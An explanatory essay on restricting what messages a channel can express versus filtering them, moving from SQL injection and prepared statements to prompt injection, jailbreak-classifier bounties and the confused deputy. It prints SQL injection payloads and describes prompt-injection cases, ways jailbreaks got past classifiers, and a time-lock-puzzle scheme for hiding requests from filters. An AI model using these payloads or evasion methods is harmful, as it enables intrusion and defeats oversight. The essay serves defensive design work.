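# Restricting what a protocol can say versus filtering its messages for harm

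## What it means for a message to be impossible rather than blocked

Programs constantly act on messages from unvetted senders. A web server acts on what a visitor types into a form, and an assistant built on a language model acts on the text of a page it has fetched. Some of these messages would do damage if the program carried them out. A designer can define the message format so narrowly that no valid message can express the damaging operation, or accept almost any message and search each one for signs of harm. Database programmers have long experience with both approaches, and the choice matters again now that language models read untrusted text and then take actions.

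A channel is any path by which one component's output can affect what another component does. The receiver is the component that acts on a message, and the designer wants to guard its powers. The permitted set is all the messages the receiver will accept and act on. A typed field is a part of a message whose possible values the designer fixes in advance, such as a whole number from 1 to 31 or a choice from a list. A free-text field can hold any string, including instructions.

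The designer of a restricted channel builds its set of permitted messages from known operations, so that the dangerous operations have no encoding. A filter inspects messages from a large, open set and rejects those it classifies as harmful.

### One login form, built three ways

Take a web page that asks for a name and a password. The server behind it has to ask a database whether the pair exists, and it asks in SQL, the standard language for database commands. The quickest way to write the program is to glue the visitor's text into a ready-made sentence. For a visitor who types "ada" and "tulip", the result is:

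`SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = 'ada' AND password = 'tulip'`

If the database returns a row, the server lets Ada in. Now someone who doesn't know the password types `' OR 'a'='a` into the password box. The first quotation mark closes the password early, and the rest becomes part of the command:

`SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = 'ada' AND password = '' OR 'a'='a'`

The letter a always equals itself, so the condition holds for every row and the visitor is let in. This is SQL injection. Su and Wassermann's *The Essence of Command Injection Attacks in Web Applications* uses almost the same example, and mentions a university whose application page had a similar flaw that let an attacker fetch the personal details of any of hundreds of thousands of applicants. The form let visitors write SQL, though the programmer thought of it as a channel for two short values, so its permitted set included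 many commands that nobody had meant to allow.

The obvious repair is a filter that rejects any input containing a quotation mark, but this also rejects names like O'Brian. The program can instead escape each quotation mark by doubling it, so that SQL reads it as an ordinary character rather than the end of the value. This stops the attack above, but it won't protect a customer number field if the form later adds one. SQL puts no quotation marks around numbers, so an attacker can type `2 OR 1=1`, which contains nothing to escape. Su and Wassermann show this attack on an online shop's page for saved payment cards, where it returns every card number in the database. OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a guide from a volunteer body for software security, marks escaping as "strongly discouraged" and says it isn't guaranteed to stop every injection.

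The third way is the prepared statement, or parameterised query. The program first sends the database a command with gaps in it:

`SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = ? AND password = ?`

The program sends the values for the gaps only afterwards. According to *PREPARE*, a manual page for the widely used database PostgreSQL, the server parses and analyses the statement when the program prepares it, then plans and runs it once the values arrive. The command's grammar is therefore fixed before the server receives the visitor's text. If the visitor types `' OR 'a'='a`, the database looks for a user whose password is that exact string, finds none, and the login fails as it would with any other wrong password.

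The attack message is impossible here because no characters in a value slot can mean "or let me in anyway". The attacker can still send the same string, and nothing detects or rejects it. The slot holds free text, which does no harm there because the database only compares it with stored passwords and never interprets it as a command. Whether a channel counts as restricted depends on what the receiver does with each field. A user name that is safe in a database table can still run as a script if the site later pastes it into a web page (an attack known as cross-site scripting).

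*SQL Injection and Prepared Statements*, a guide on a personal website and so a weak source, warns that some database drivers only emulate prepared statements. Such a driver escapes the values, inserts them into the query text and sends the server one finished string. A programmer using it is still relying on escaping, perhaps without knowing it.

Even a true prepared statement covers only values. PostgreSQL's manual explains that substitution can put data into a command but cannot change which database objects the command refers to. So if the login page keeps staff and customers in separate tables and lets the visitor pick one, the programmer can't use a question mark in place of the table's name. Pasting in the visitor's choice as text would make SQL injection possible again. OWASP advises rethinking the design or, failing that, mapping the visitor's choice onto table names already written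 in the program. One value selects the staff table, another selects the customer table, and anything else raises an error, which makes the choice a typed field. Sort order can be handled the same way, with the program converting the visitor's choice to true or false and then picking the SQL keyword itself.

Prepared statements also don't stop someone from submitting a valid value they aren't authorized to use. If a page shows the balance of whichever account number the browser sends, a visitor can send somebody else's number. The query is well formed, so the database will answer it. OWASP's remedy is to limit what the application's own database account can access.

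### The difference in symbols

Let L be the set of permitted strings and H the set of harmful ones, meaning those that would make this receiver do something its owner wants to rule out. The channel is safe against H when L and H have no member in common (L ∩ H = ∅).

With a restricted channel, the designer picks operations whose effects are known and defines L as everything those operations can express. The login example has a single operation, "find the id that goes with this name and this password", and L contains one message for each possible pair of strings. L is infinite, but the designer can cover all of it with one argument before the first visitor arrives: whatever the two strings are, the database only looks up that pair.

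With a filter, the designer starts with A, the set of all possible messages, and removes D, the set of messages the filter detects, so the set of allowed messages is L = A − D. This is safe only if D contains every message in H, the set of harmful messages. To know that it does, the designer would need a full description of H, which nobody has.

A restricted channel differs from a filter in how the designer arrived at the permitted set L, and therefore in what anyone can know about L. As sets, the two are the same kind of object. A filter also defines a permitted set, A − D, and any restricted channel can be redescribed as a filter that detects everything outside L. Nobody can therefore tell the two approaches apart from a list of accepted messages.

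*Guns and Butter* (Hansen and Patterson, 2005) proposes writing a sublanguage of SQL that keeps only the grammar rules needed to produce the intended login query, with plain strings in the two value positions. Every sentence of the sublanguage is valid SQL, and every one is safe because the grammar can generate only the intended query. The program assembles the query by joining strings, as before, then runs it through a parser for the sublanguage and discards it if the parse fails. The parser rejects messages at a checkpoint, as a filter does, but this still counts as a restricted channel because the designer built the sublanguage from sentences with a known effect and never had to describe an attack.

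A list of allowed characters is the reverse case. It sounds restrictive, and it also builds messages from permitted parts, but those parts are characters, which have no effect of their own. Letters, digits, spaces and an equals sign are enough to write the SQL injection `2 OR 1=1`. OWASP therefore cautions that validated data is not necessarily safe to paste into a query.

A parser for a small grammar quickly and exactly determines whether a message belongs to L. A filter can be quick too, but it checks whether the message resembles something on a list of bad things, while its designer cares whether the message belongs to H. Hansen and Patterson trace much of the trouble to tools that are too weak for the language. Regular expressions, the pattern notation most programmers use, cannot recognise even the set of strings made of some number of a's followed by the same number of b's, because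 matching the two halves requires unbounded memory. Recognising SQL requires a tool at least powerful enough to do this. Developers at the time were arguing over whether their regular expressions should admit known good input or exclude known bad input. Hansen and Patterson thought the argument missed the point, because a tool that can't recognise the language will either accept some bad input or reject some good input.

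Su and Wassermann define a SQL query as an attack when a piece of user input in it fails to form a complete grammatical unit of a permitted kind, such as one number or one string. If a visitor types `2 OR 1=1` and the query becomes `cardtype = 2 OR 1=1`, the 2 belongs to one comparison and the 1=1 to another, so the input is not a single unit. Their tool, SQLCHECK, puts markers around each input, keeps them there when the input is inserted into the query, and parses the result with a grammar that accepts only whole units between markers. They tested it on five web applications, each written in two programming languages. For each language it stopped all 18,424 attack requests and passed all 3,824 legitimate ones, at roughly three milliseconds per query. The attacks came from an independent research group's collection of real exploits, but nobody had written them to defeat SQLCHECK. Su and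 Wassermann concede that an attacker could find the four-letter markers by trying every combination, which is a weakness in the marking rather than the grammar, and they describe a fix.

The third difference is whether the checker and the receiver interpret the message the same way. Escaping code relies on its author's understanding of how the database parses text, and in the card example the author wrongly assumed that a value always sits between quotation marks. Engineers use the term "parser differential" for cases where two components interpret the same bytes as different messages. The prepared statement avoids this particular differential because there is no separate checker. The database parses the command itself, once, before it has the values.

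Last, a message that nobody foresaw falls outside L in a restricted channel, so the receiver refuses it. If the message was legitimate, the designer is likely to learn of the mistake promptly, because a user complains, and can then add an operation. In a filter, an unforeseen message falls outside D, so the receiver acts on it. If it was harmful, the traffic may look ordinary for a long time, so the designer is unlikely to learn of the mistake promptly.

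A restricted channel is not safe by definition. Its safety depends heavily on whether its operations really are "operations whose effects are known". Hansen and Patterson admit that programmers can write bad sublanguages, and that no general procedure can decide whether a sublanguage meets its author's expectations. Su and Wassermann assume that the fixed part of the query matches the programmer's intent, so a template that deletes a table by mistake does not count as a fault under their definition.

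### From databases to language models

Patterson and others soon took the idea well beyond SQL. In *Security Applications of Formal Language Theory*, Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues (2011) used formal grammars to analyse security flaws in common protocols, and described a way to build attacks from differences between two parsers. The research programme around this work is called language-theoretic security, or LangSec. Its central claim, as stated on its website, LANGSEC, is that developers should treat all valid inputs to a program as a formal language and the input-handling code as a recogniser for that language, which decides whether an input belongs to it before any other code uses that input. LangSec calls the permitted set the input language and has its own rules for writing the parsers. The claim is broader than anything the SQL work had shown, since it covers every file format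 and network protocol, but the login form is a fair small example of it.

In September 2022, the developer Riley Goodside demonstrated the same mixing of commands and data in GPT-3, then OpenAI's main language model. When an application asked GPT-3 to translate a sentence into French, and the sentence contained an instruction to ignore the request and print something else, the model followed that instruction. Willison (2022), in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, named the attack and noted that the application had joined its own instructions to a stranger's text, just as the vulnerable login page builds its query. In prompt injection, someone plants instructions in material that a language model reads as data, and the model follows them. The attacker need not use the application. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written in December 2025 for Britain's National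 Cyber Security Centre, David C describes a recruiter's system that asks a model to score CVs, and a candidate who hides a line in the CV telling the model to approve it.

Willison first hoped for a model interface that worked like a prepared statement, with one parameter for the instructions and others for named blocks of data. A reader told him that one of OpenAI's models already took separate "instruction" and "input" parameters. Injection through the input still worked. By April 2023 Willison had added a note calling parameterised prompts "extremely difficult, if not impossible" on the current architecture.

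A language model has no value slot. It receives one sequence of tokens (words or fragments of words) and predicts what comes next, and every token can influence the prediction. An interface may label some tokens as data, but the label is just more input that can influence the prediction. In the database, by contrast, the code that compares passwords cannot pass them back to the code that parses commands. David C therefore concludes that prompt injection may never be fully preventable in the way SQL injection is. His argument is based on how the models work and is not a proof. Training can make a model much less likely to obey planted text, and he lists it among the active lines of research. But training only lowers the rate of failure, whereas the question marks in the login page's query prevent a password from being parsed as a command at all.

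Most early defences were filters or forms of escaping, and they failed. Goodside suggested putting the untrusted sentence in quotation marks, formatted as a programming string, but another developer soon got around this with text that imitated the end of one translation and the start of the next. Others proposed asking a second model whether an injection had taken place. Willison reproduces an exchange in which the planted text included an instruction for the detector to report that nothing had happened, and the detector followed it. These tricks were used on 2022 models and are weak evidence about current ones, but the underlying difficulty remains. In *I don’t know how to solve prompt injection* (2022), Willison quotes a fellow engineer's remark that the cures for SQL injection work by correcting a mistake in syntax, and that a prompt has no formal syntax to correct. Willison would not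 be satisfied with a protection that caught 99 per cent of attacks, because attackers would keep trying until they found one that it missed. David C makes a similar point about lists of forbidden phrases, which fail because an attacker can reword the same instruction in endless ways. Infosecurity Magazine's *Infosecurity Europe* (2026) reports that the OWASP contributor Ariel Fogel was still describing prompt injection as an unsolved problem of architecture at a London trade conference in 2026.

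If the model cannot separate instructions from data, the restriction has to go somewhere else. David C recommends treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy", a component that outsiders can manipulate into misusing its own powers, and surrounding it with ordinary deterministic code that limits what it can do. He names a 2025 publication by researchers at Google and ETH Zurich as one of the first major ones to take this approach. In this report's terms, the designer defines a permitted set for the program that carries out the model's output rather than for the model itself.

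A help desk might use a model to read messages from customers who are locked out of their accounts. The program behind the model accepts only three answers: send a reset link to the address on file, ask for more details, or pass the case to a person. Designers call a model that reads untrusted text and has no power to act a quarantined model. A hostile message may well make the model choose the wrong answer, but it can't get the reset link sent to the attacker's own address, because none of the three answers includes an option to send it there.

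## Deciding whether to restrict a channel or filter it

The help desk can work with three answers because its designers know in advance everything it needs to do. A chatbot that explains chemistry is harder to protect because its users want free text and nobody can list its useful answers beforehand. A few of its possible answers would help someone make a nerve agent, so its owner will have to filter its messages.

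The best argument for restriction is that it works no matter who the sender is. A designer who has checked every permitted operation doesn't need to know how many attackers there are or how often they will try. The best argument for filtering is that legitimate senders can still ask for things the designer never thought of. Whether that freedom is worth having depends on how many harmful messages the filter lets through and how many legitimate ones it refuses.

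### What no filter can work out

Some messages contain programs, and whether a program is harmful depends on what it does when it runs. No general method can work that out from the program's text. Suppose a checker could read any program and always report correctly whether it will delete a file. For any program P that never touches files, we could write a longer program that runs P and then deletes a file. The longer program deletes the file exactly when P finishes, so we could use the checker to find out whether P ever finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can determine this for every program. Rice's theorem, from 1953, extends the result to every property of a program's behaviour that some programs have and others lack.

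*LLM Censorship* (Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues, 2023) applies the theorem to language models, which both read and write code. Whether a program is harmful is undecidable, meaning that no algorithm can pass every harmless program and stop every harmful one. The theorem assumes unlimited memory and arbitrary programs. Glukhov and colleagues concede that it doesn't strictly apply to real computers and messages, which are finite, but they point to the long struggle to detect malware as a sign that the difficulty remains in practice.

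Rice's theorem still allows a checker that refuses every program it cannot prove safe, though it will refuse some harmless programs too. A designer can also shrink the programming language until the question becomes easy to answer. For instance, every program finishes in a language without loops or recursion. Both remedies move the design towards a restricted channel.

A separate result in the same work covers messages of limited length. If a user tells a model to shift every letter of its answer three places along the alphabet, the answer reaches the filter as gibberish, but the user can easily decode it. Glukhov and colleagues assume that the model can apply any reversible transformation the user describes, and that the filter has no information about which one the user chose. They also require the filter to treat a disguised harmful text as harmful whenever the recipient can undo the disguise.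 For any innocent output, such as a recipe for lentil soup, some reversible code turns a harmful text into exactly that output, and the user might hold the key. Unless the filter permits everything, it must therefore refuse the recipe and, by the same argument, every other string.

The proof is sound, but its standard for the filter is very strict, since the filter must refuse anything that could be harmful under some code. An attacker who wants a text he has never seen can't easily design a code that turns it into a soup recipe. He will use a general-purpose code, whose output usually looks like gibberish, which a filter can refuse. Glukhov and colleagues also note that the proof doesn't cover a filter that checks the user's input together with the output, although Rice's theorem still applies to such a filter.

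### When the filter has less computing power than the model

Refusing gibberish won't help if the hidden message looks like ordinary prose. *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) shows how to hide a message in such prose from any filter that runs much faster than the model it protects. Most practical filters are that much faster, since few operators want to pay for a second model as large as the first.

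The construction uses a time-lock puzzle, which anyone can solve, but only after a set amount of computing that extra machines can't speed up. The puzzle's author picks two large primes p and q, multiplies them to get n, and chooses a random number r and a number of steps t. The answer is

r^(2^t) mod n,

the remainder on dividing by n after squaring r repeatedly, t times. A solver has to do the squarings one after another. The author knows p and q and can take a shortcut, first reducing the exponent to e = 2^t mod (p − 1)(q − 1) and then computing r^e mod n.

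With toy numbers p = 3, q = 11, r = 2 and t = 5, a solver squares r repeatedly modulo 33, five times in all, and gets 4, 16, 25, 31 and 4. The author reduces 2^5 = 32 modulo 20, gets 12, and computes 2^12 mod 33, which is also 4. With t in the billions, the shortcut saves almost all the work.

The attack then runs as follows:

1. The attacker encrypts a harmful request, using the puzzle's answer as the key. With some extra preparation, the puzzle and the encrypted request together look like random bits.
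2. A program that writes innocent prompts normally uses random bits to choose between plausible next words. The attacker gives it these bits instead, and it writes an ordinary-looking prompt.
3. The model reconstructs the bits from the prompt, solves the puzzle, decrypts the request and carries it out.

A filter that doesn't have time to do the squarings can't distinguish this prompt from an innocent one. The theorem assumes that time-lock puzzles exist, that the filter is significantly faster than the model, and that there are many different innocent prompts. It also depends on a model built to search its prompts for puzzles and follow the instructions it finds in them. Ball and colleagues admit that such a model is contrived, but reply that contrived weaknesses have led to real thefts before, citing the 2016 attack on the Ethereum blockchain, which cost victims more than 60 million dollars.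 The example is a fair warning but not evidence that any deployed model behaves this way.

The theorem doesn't rule out a filter that is about as slow as the model, or one that reads the model's internal state. It also doesn't apply to a channel with only a few possible messages, because those messages can't encode a puzzle. Ball and colleagues also prove versions that rule out every filter running in polynomial time (roughly, any that is practical on large inputs), but these require the model to cooperate with the attacker through a shared secret or a published key.

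Their theorem on output filters shows that for any model there is another whose outputs count as harmful, yet no efficient filter can tell those outputs apart from the original's, even with more computing power than the model has. The proof measures harm with an "oracle", a mathematical stand-in for what happens in the world, which neither the model nor the filter can consult. The oracle finds the harm by solving a puzzle that would take exponentially longer to solve than the model takes to run, so a human reader couldn't extract anything dangerous from such a text. The theorem is therefore a better model of plans whose consequences nobody can foresee than of weapon recipes hidden in prose.

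These proofs rule out a general guarantee for a filter over free text. They give no failure rate for any particular filter.

### What the error rates add up to

Suppose a service receives 1,000,000 messages a day, of which 10 are hostile. Its filter detects 99% of hostile messages and raises a false alarm on 0.1% of the rest, which would be very good for a filter that reads prose. On an average day, it catches 9.9 hostile messages and flags about 1,000 innocent ones, so only about 1 in 100 alarms is real.

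If π is the share of messages that are hostile, d the detection rate and f the false-alarm rate, the share of alarms that are real is

dπ / (dπ + f(1 − π)).

When π is tiny, the result depends almost entirely on f, and raising d from 99% to 100% barely changes it. For half the alarms to be real, the filter would have to flag no more than about one innocent message in 100,000. If the service blocks every flagged message, it blocks messages from about 1,000 legitimate senders each day. If it sends flagged messages to human reviewers, the reviewers read about a hundred innocent messages for each attack and will probably start to skim.

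A determined attacker can also try more than once. If the filter misses 1% of attacks and the tries are independent, the chance that at least one of n tries succeeds is 1 − 0.99^n. That chance reaches 50% after 69 tries and 95% after 300, and a script can send 300 in an afternoon. If the miss rate is cut to 0.1%, the attacker needs 693 tries for a 50% chance, about ten times as many.

Real tries aren't independent. If a filter gives identical text an identical score, resending a rejected message achieves nothing, and slight rewordings of a failed attack tend to fail together. Both help the defender, but an attacker who sees which attempts fail can improve the next ones, and an attack that gets through once will probably get through again. The defender can lower the attacker's odds by closing accounts that keep triggering the filter. The 1% is usually measured on a fixed set of known attacks,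 so it may be far too low for a new one. The figures of 69 and 300 therefore show the scale of the problem but don't predict how many tries an attack will take.

### A filter that mostly held

Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, has published detailed tests of free-text filters against jailbreaks, prompts that get a model to answer questions its makers trained it to refuse. In *Constitutional Classifiers*, Sharma, Tong and colleagues (2025) placed one filter on the user's prompt and another on the model's answer. The second filter can cut the answer off while the model is still writing it. Both filters are language models. To train them, the team wrote a "constitution", a list in plain English of permitted kinds of content, such as explanations of school chemistry, and forbidden kinds, such as instructions for purifying restricted chemicals. A model then generated examples of each kind,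 and the team expanded the set by translating the examples, paraphrasing them and rewriting them as known jailbreaks.

The team invited 405 people to attack a prototype, and about 183 actively took part. They tried to get answers to ten questions about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons, and could earn up to $15,000 for a universal jailbreak, meaning one technique that works on nearly all questions in a field. An answer counted if it scored at least half as high for detail as an unguarded model's answer. The attackers spent an estimated 4,720 hours (90% confidence interval 3,242 to 7,417) and submitted 113 reports, none of which had answers to all ten questions. One report's apparent success came from a bug in the surrounding code, which let through up to 128 more tokens after the filter had flagged the answer.

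The prototype also refused about 44% of ordinary traffic on Claude.ai, which made it unusable as a product. An improved version raised refusals by 0.38 percentage points and used 23.7% more computation. It cut the success rate of automatically generated attacks from 86% to 4.4%. But this version covered only chemical weapons, and Sharma and colleagues did not repeat the human bounty on it. The same method, trained on the prototype's broader constitution, wrongly refused about 1.74% of traffic.

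A public test followed in February 2025. According to Anthropic's announcement, *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025), 339 people spent about 3,700 hours and more than 300,000 chats trying to get answers to eight chemical-weapons questions. The filter held for five days. Over the next two, four participants got detailed answers to all eight questions, one of them with a universal jailbreak. Anthropic points out that participants got immediate feedback from an automatic grader on whether an answer was good enough, and that the company left the filter unchanged all week but could have patched it in real service. Both points are reasonable, though a real attacker would have longer than a week.

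Willison objected to the target because a jailbreak that worked on only some of the questions would still reveal a worrying gap. By that measure the prototype did less well. Nine reports answered more than six of the ten questions at the half-detail standard, although none answered more than five at the full detail of an unguarded model. Sharma and colleagues add that many high-scoring answers were padded and earned their points through length.

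Sharma and colleagues defend the focus on universal jailbreaks with a simple model in which making a weapon takes many steps and the attacker needs help with each. If he has a 60% chance of getting a detailed answer at each step, his chance of getting detailed answers to all ten steps is 0.6^10, or about 0.6%. This calculation assumes that the steps are independent, which makes the defense look stronger than it is. They call the assumption a simplification, and their own results show that the questions varied widely in difficulty, with four successful reports on the hardest and more than thirty on the easiest.

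Later attackers got past these filters by scattering a request across harmless-looking pieces, or by having the model answer in a code that made no sense without the prompt. Glukhov and colleagues had described the second weakness in theory. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) addresses these attacks with an "exchange classifier", which reads the answer together with the prompt. Disguising a request also makes the model's answers less accurate. On a set of difficult science questions, Claude Opus 4 scored 74.2% normally, but 32.3% and 49% when the questions were posed through two such attacks.

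Their production version first runs a probe on every exchange and passes the most suspicious 5.5% to a larger classifier. The probe is a calculation on the model's internal activations that takes very little compute. Because it uses those activations, Ball and colleagues' theorem on prompt filters doesn't apply to it. The probe can be allowed many false alarms because a flagged exchange gets a second check instead of a refusal.

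| System | Computing cost (first generation = 100) | High-risk vulnerabilities found | Ordinary traffic refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| First generation, as rebuilt for the comparison | 100 | 13 in 695,000 attack queries | 0.073% |
| Exchange classifier | 150 | 2 in 226,000 | 0.038% |
| Two-stage version without the probe | 27.8 | 5 in 569,000 | 0.036% |
| Production version | 3.5 | 1 in 198,000 | 0.050% |

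A high-risk vulnerability is an attack that got the model to answer more than five of eight target questions in at least half the detail of an unguarded model. The reduction in compute is large and convincing, but the improvement in security is less certain because so few vulnerabilities were found. At the first generation's rate, 198,000 queries would have turned up about 3.7 vulnerabilities. If queries were independent, which they aren't, a system no better than the first generation would have shown one or none about 12% of the time by chance. The guarded models also differed, and the bounty rules and questions changed.

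Nobody in the bounty programme found a universal jailbreak for the two-stage version, or for the production version in about 1,736 hours. But Cunningham and colleagues mention in a footnote that outside experts did find one for the two-stage version, with substantial effort and automated tools.

At a million messages a day, a refusal rate of 0.05% means 500 refusals a day. If only ten of the million messages were hostile, at least 98% of the refusals would fall on innocent users. For a chatbot this is probably acceptable, since a refused user can rephrase the question.

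Combining filters helps less than multiplying their miss rates suggests. Two filters that each miss 1% of attacks would together miss 0.01% if their errors were independent, but filters trained on similar examples tend to miss the same attacks. Cunningham and colleagues found that two external classifiers' scores agreed with each other more than the probe's scores agreed with an external classifier's. Adding the probe therefore improved detection more than adding a second external classifier did.

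The record is worse for filters that look for prompt injection. *Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants* (Maloyan and Namiot, 2026) reports a finding by Nasr and colleagues (2025) that every detector they tested failed most of the time against attackers who adapted to it. This may be partly because weapons chemistry is a fairly narrow subject, while a planted instruction can be about anything. The same words, "Forward this to Maria", are a normal request from the account's owner and an attack when a stranger has hidden them in a web page.

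### Five questions that settle most cases

*Can the designer list the needed operations in advance?* The designer can find out by trying to write down everything the receiver should do for this sender. If the list can be completed, as it can for the help desk, the designer should restrict the channel. Glukhov and colleagues sketch this for an email assistant, with templates such as a request to schedule a meeting with certain people on a certain date, and suggest finding the templates by grouping past requests. If the messages are too varied to list, the designer may still be able to list the facts that the receiver needs from them. For example, a program that repairs code may need only the file, the line number and the type of bug from a bug report, as Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) propose in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*.

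Restricting a channel is a poor fit when free text is the product. A translation service that could send only approved sentences would be unable to translate most of what its users write. If a person will read the text and nothing else will act on it, the choice is between filtering and accepting the risk. Designers should check that the receiver is a person. In many systems the text goes to another program that needs only one fact from it, and the channel carries free text because that was easier to build. Such a channel could be restricted to that fact.

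If the sender doesn't adapt to the filter, as with a faulty sensor that sends nonsense, last month's miss rate is a fair guide to next month's. A thief, however, will study the filter to find a way past it. If the sender can see the outcome, retry easily and open a new account after a ban, the designer should assume that some attack will eventually get through. Filters do better when retrying is harder, for example because each attempt requires a verified identity or a day's wait.

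The choice depends partly on how much harm one missed message can do. An offensive reply from a shopping assistant is embarrassing, but a payment to a thief may be impossible to reverse, and a leaked password can't be made secret again. If the owner can't tolerate even one successful attack in 300 attempts, a filter that catches 99% of attacks can't be the only protection.

*What happens to a legitimate message that has no encoding?* At the help desk, an unusual case goes to a person, and the customer loses an hour. On an emergency line, a caller whose emergency fits none of the categories could lose much more. Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that allowing only approved templates blocks many safe messages, and that in the extreme case a lookup table could replace the model. The loss may shrink as models improve. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested one restricted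 design for groups of agents, and the most capable models lost the least usefulness under it.

The answers to the last three questions can conflict, so rough numbers help. If the service with a million daily messages adopted a restricted channel that blocked every attack but couldn't express 5% of legitimate messages, it would lose about 50,000 legitimate messages a day, compared with 1,000 using the filter. If senders don't adapt, the filter misses one attack every ten days, so restriction is worthwhile only if one successful attack is worse than losing 490,000 legitimate messages. If senders do adapt and all ten attacks a day get through, the break-even point falls to 4,900. Restriction would then easily be worthwhile for bank transfers, but probably not for a forum's comment box.

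### Using both, and why typed values are easier to filter

Many systems need both restriction and filtering, on different channels. The help desk's model can send the account system one of its three answers and also write a few friendly sentences to the customer. The account system acts only on that answer. The sentences go through a filter before the customer reads them, and no program acts on them. Filtering the incoming messages is also useful, because the model then reads fewer hostile ones and the filter's alarms can reveal an attack. The risk is that the team starts to rely on this filter and later adds a free-text "notes" field for the account system to act on.

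A filter is also useful behind a restricted channel, because valid requests can still do harm. Filtering is much easier there. Suppose the help desk can also handle refunds, and each message consists of an action from a list of three, a whole number of pounds from 0 to 200 and a reason from a list of ten. That allows 3 × 201 × 10 = 6,030 messages, so a program can test the filter on every one before launch. A 200-character note in lower-case letters and spaces has about 10^286 possible versions, many with the same meaning, and testing can cover only a tiny fraction of them.

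With the typed message, an attacker can't reword a £150 refund, translate it or hide it in a poem. The rule "send refunds over £100 to a person" only compares two numbers, so Rice's theorem is no obstacle, and the message is too small to hide a time-lock puzzle. Deciding whether a £90 refund is honest still takes judgement, and the base-rate arithmetic still applies, but the filter can use the account's history and the amount without having to interpret the message.

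## Designing the set of permitted messages

The typed refund message at the help desk has 6,030 versions, including some that no shop would grant, such as a request for £200 back on a £15 lamp. A filter could catch that request by looking up the lamp's price. But if the shop can look up the price, the message doesn't need to include an amount, so the designer can remove that field instead of having a filter check it.

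Much of the work of designing a permitted set consists of removals like this. A designer can go about it in seven steps:

1. List everything the receiver can do.
2. Strike out whatever this sender never needs.
3. Turn the rest into named operations.
4. Let the receiver compute every value it can.
5. Give each remaining field the smallest type that will do.
6. Replace names with references that the sender already holds.
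7. Fix which message may follow which.

Following the steps in this order saves work, because a designer who starts with the types may spend a day choosing limits for an amount field that they would have deleted in step 4.

### A refund assistant with 41 messages

Suppose an online shop uses a language model to read customers' emails, and the model can ask the shop's payment service, the receiver, for a refund. The designer has to assume that a hostile email can make the model send any message the format allows. One customer, Ada, has four recent orders: a kettle for £40, a lamp for £15, a rug for £120 and some towels for £25.

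The payment service can charge a card, refund an order, send money to any bank account, replace a customer's saved card and export the sales records. The designer should list what the software can do, including functions the shop has never used, because an attacker might use them. The assistant needs only refunds, so the designer crosses out the rest. As one of LANGSEC's slogans puts it, "The power that is not there cannot be hijacked." If a customer needs a bank transfer once a year, a person can make it.

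Two named operations remain, "refund" and "no refund". A general operation such as "run this transaction" would again allow everything the designer had removed, because the transaction could be a bank transfer. "No refund" is a separate message so that the service can distinguish a refusal from a crash.

To pay a refund, the service needs the order, the amount, the currency and the card. It already has a record of the lamp's price, the currency and the card used, so the message leaves them out. The assistant only has to choose between a full and a half refund, the two options the shop's policy allows. The shop also wants a reason for its records, and five reasons cover nearly every case.

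That leaves the order. The assistant could copy an order number from the email, but the number might belong to somebody else. Instead, ordinary code looks up the account that the email came from and gives the payment service a table with Ada's four orders in slots 1 to 4. The assistant sees a short description of each order and replies with a slot number. Each slot works once, and the service accepts one message per email. The whole format is:

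`refund(order: 1 | 2 | 3 | 4, reason: damaged | faulty | late | wrong item | unwanted, share: full | half)`

`no refund`

This makes 4 × 5 × 2 + 1 = 41 messages. Replacing the slot with an eight-digit order number would raise that to just over a billion, nearly all about other people's orders.

Suppose an attacker uses an email to take complete control of the model and make it try to send £500 to the attacker's bank account. The model cannot express this request because no message has a field for an account. The designer instead had the service that receives the message determine the payee by looking up the card in the order's record.

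The email might instead ask for £500 on the lamp. The most the assistant can send is "full", and the service calculates the sum from the stored price. The assistant can't pass on the £500 figure because its message now specifies one of two shares instead of an amount.

The single-use slot prevents a second refund on the same order. The service has to pay the refund and mark the order as refunded in one indivisible step, or two copies of a message that arrive together might both succeed. Ada may also write again tomorrow and get a new table, so the code that fills the table must leave out refunded orders. After one refund, her next table holds three orders and the permitted set shrinks to 31 messages. After four refunds, only "no refund" is left. Under this rule, a customer who accepted half the price of a rug and later finds it beyond repair can't get the other half from the assistant, so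 a person has to deal with that case.

The assistant can still grant a refund that Ada doesn't deserve. But these four orders can cost the shop at most £200, however many emails she sends. The money can only go back to the card she paid with, so someone who forges her email address gains nothing.

### Why a reference is safer than a name

The "confusable deputy" in David C's advice on language models goes back to an incident that Hardy describes in *The Confused Deputy* (1988). Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers in the 1970s, let customers run a compiler, a program that translates other programs into machine code, and choose a file for its debugging output. The compiler also kept usage statistics in a system directory, so Tymshare had given it permission to write to any file there, including the billing records. One customer chose the billing file, which he had no permission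 to write to himself. The compiler did have permission, so it overwrote the bills.

Hardy considers several fixes that amount to filtering file names. The compiler could refuse names in other directories, but customers had good reasons to use them. It could refuse names in the system directory, but some customers might have legitimate access to files there. It could refuse the billing file by name, but someone would then have to add a rule for every new sensitive file. The rule for when a program could open a file grew to contain fourteen "ands" and "ors". Tymshare then let programs declare whether they were using the customer's permission or their own, but some programs soon needed more than two sources of permission.

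The compiler had permission from two sources, and a file name doesn't show which of them applies. Hardy's solution is the capability, an unforgeable reference that both identifies a resource and grants the right to use it. The compiler would hold a capability for the statistics file, and the customer would give it another for his output file. The customer has no capability for the billing file, so he can't direct the output there, and the compiler doesn't need to check any names.

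Modern operating systems use something similar called a file descriptor, a small number that stands for an open file. UT Austin's lecture slides *The Confused Deputy* solve Hardy's case by having a separate program with limited permissions open the debugging file and pass the file's descriptor to the compiler. Guessing a descriptor such as 3 doesn't give a program any extra access, because the operating system looks the number up in a table that belongs to that program, and the program can't add a file to the table that it has no right to open. Ada's slots work the same way. A long random code would also work as a reference, but the model might leak it in a reply to a customer, and unlike a slot number, it could then be used by someone else.

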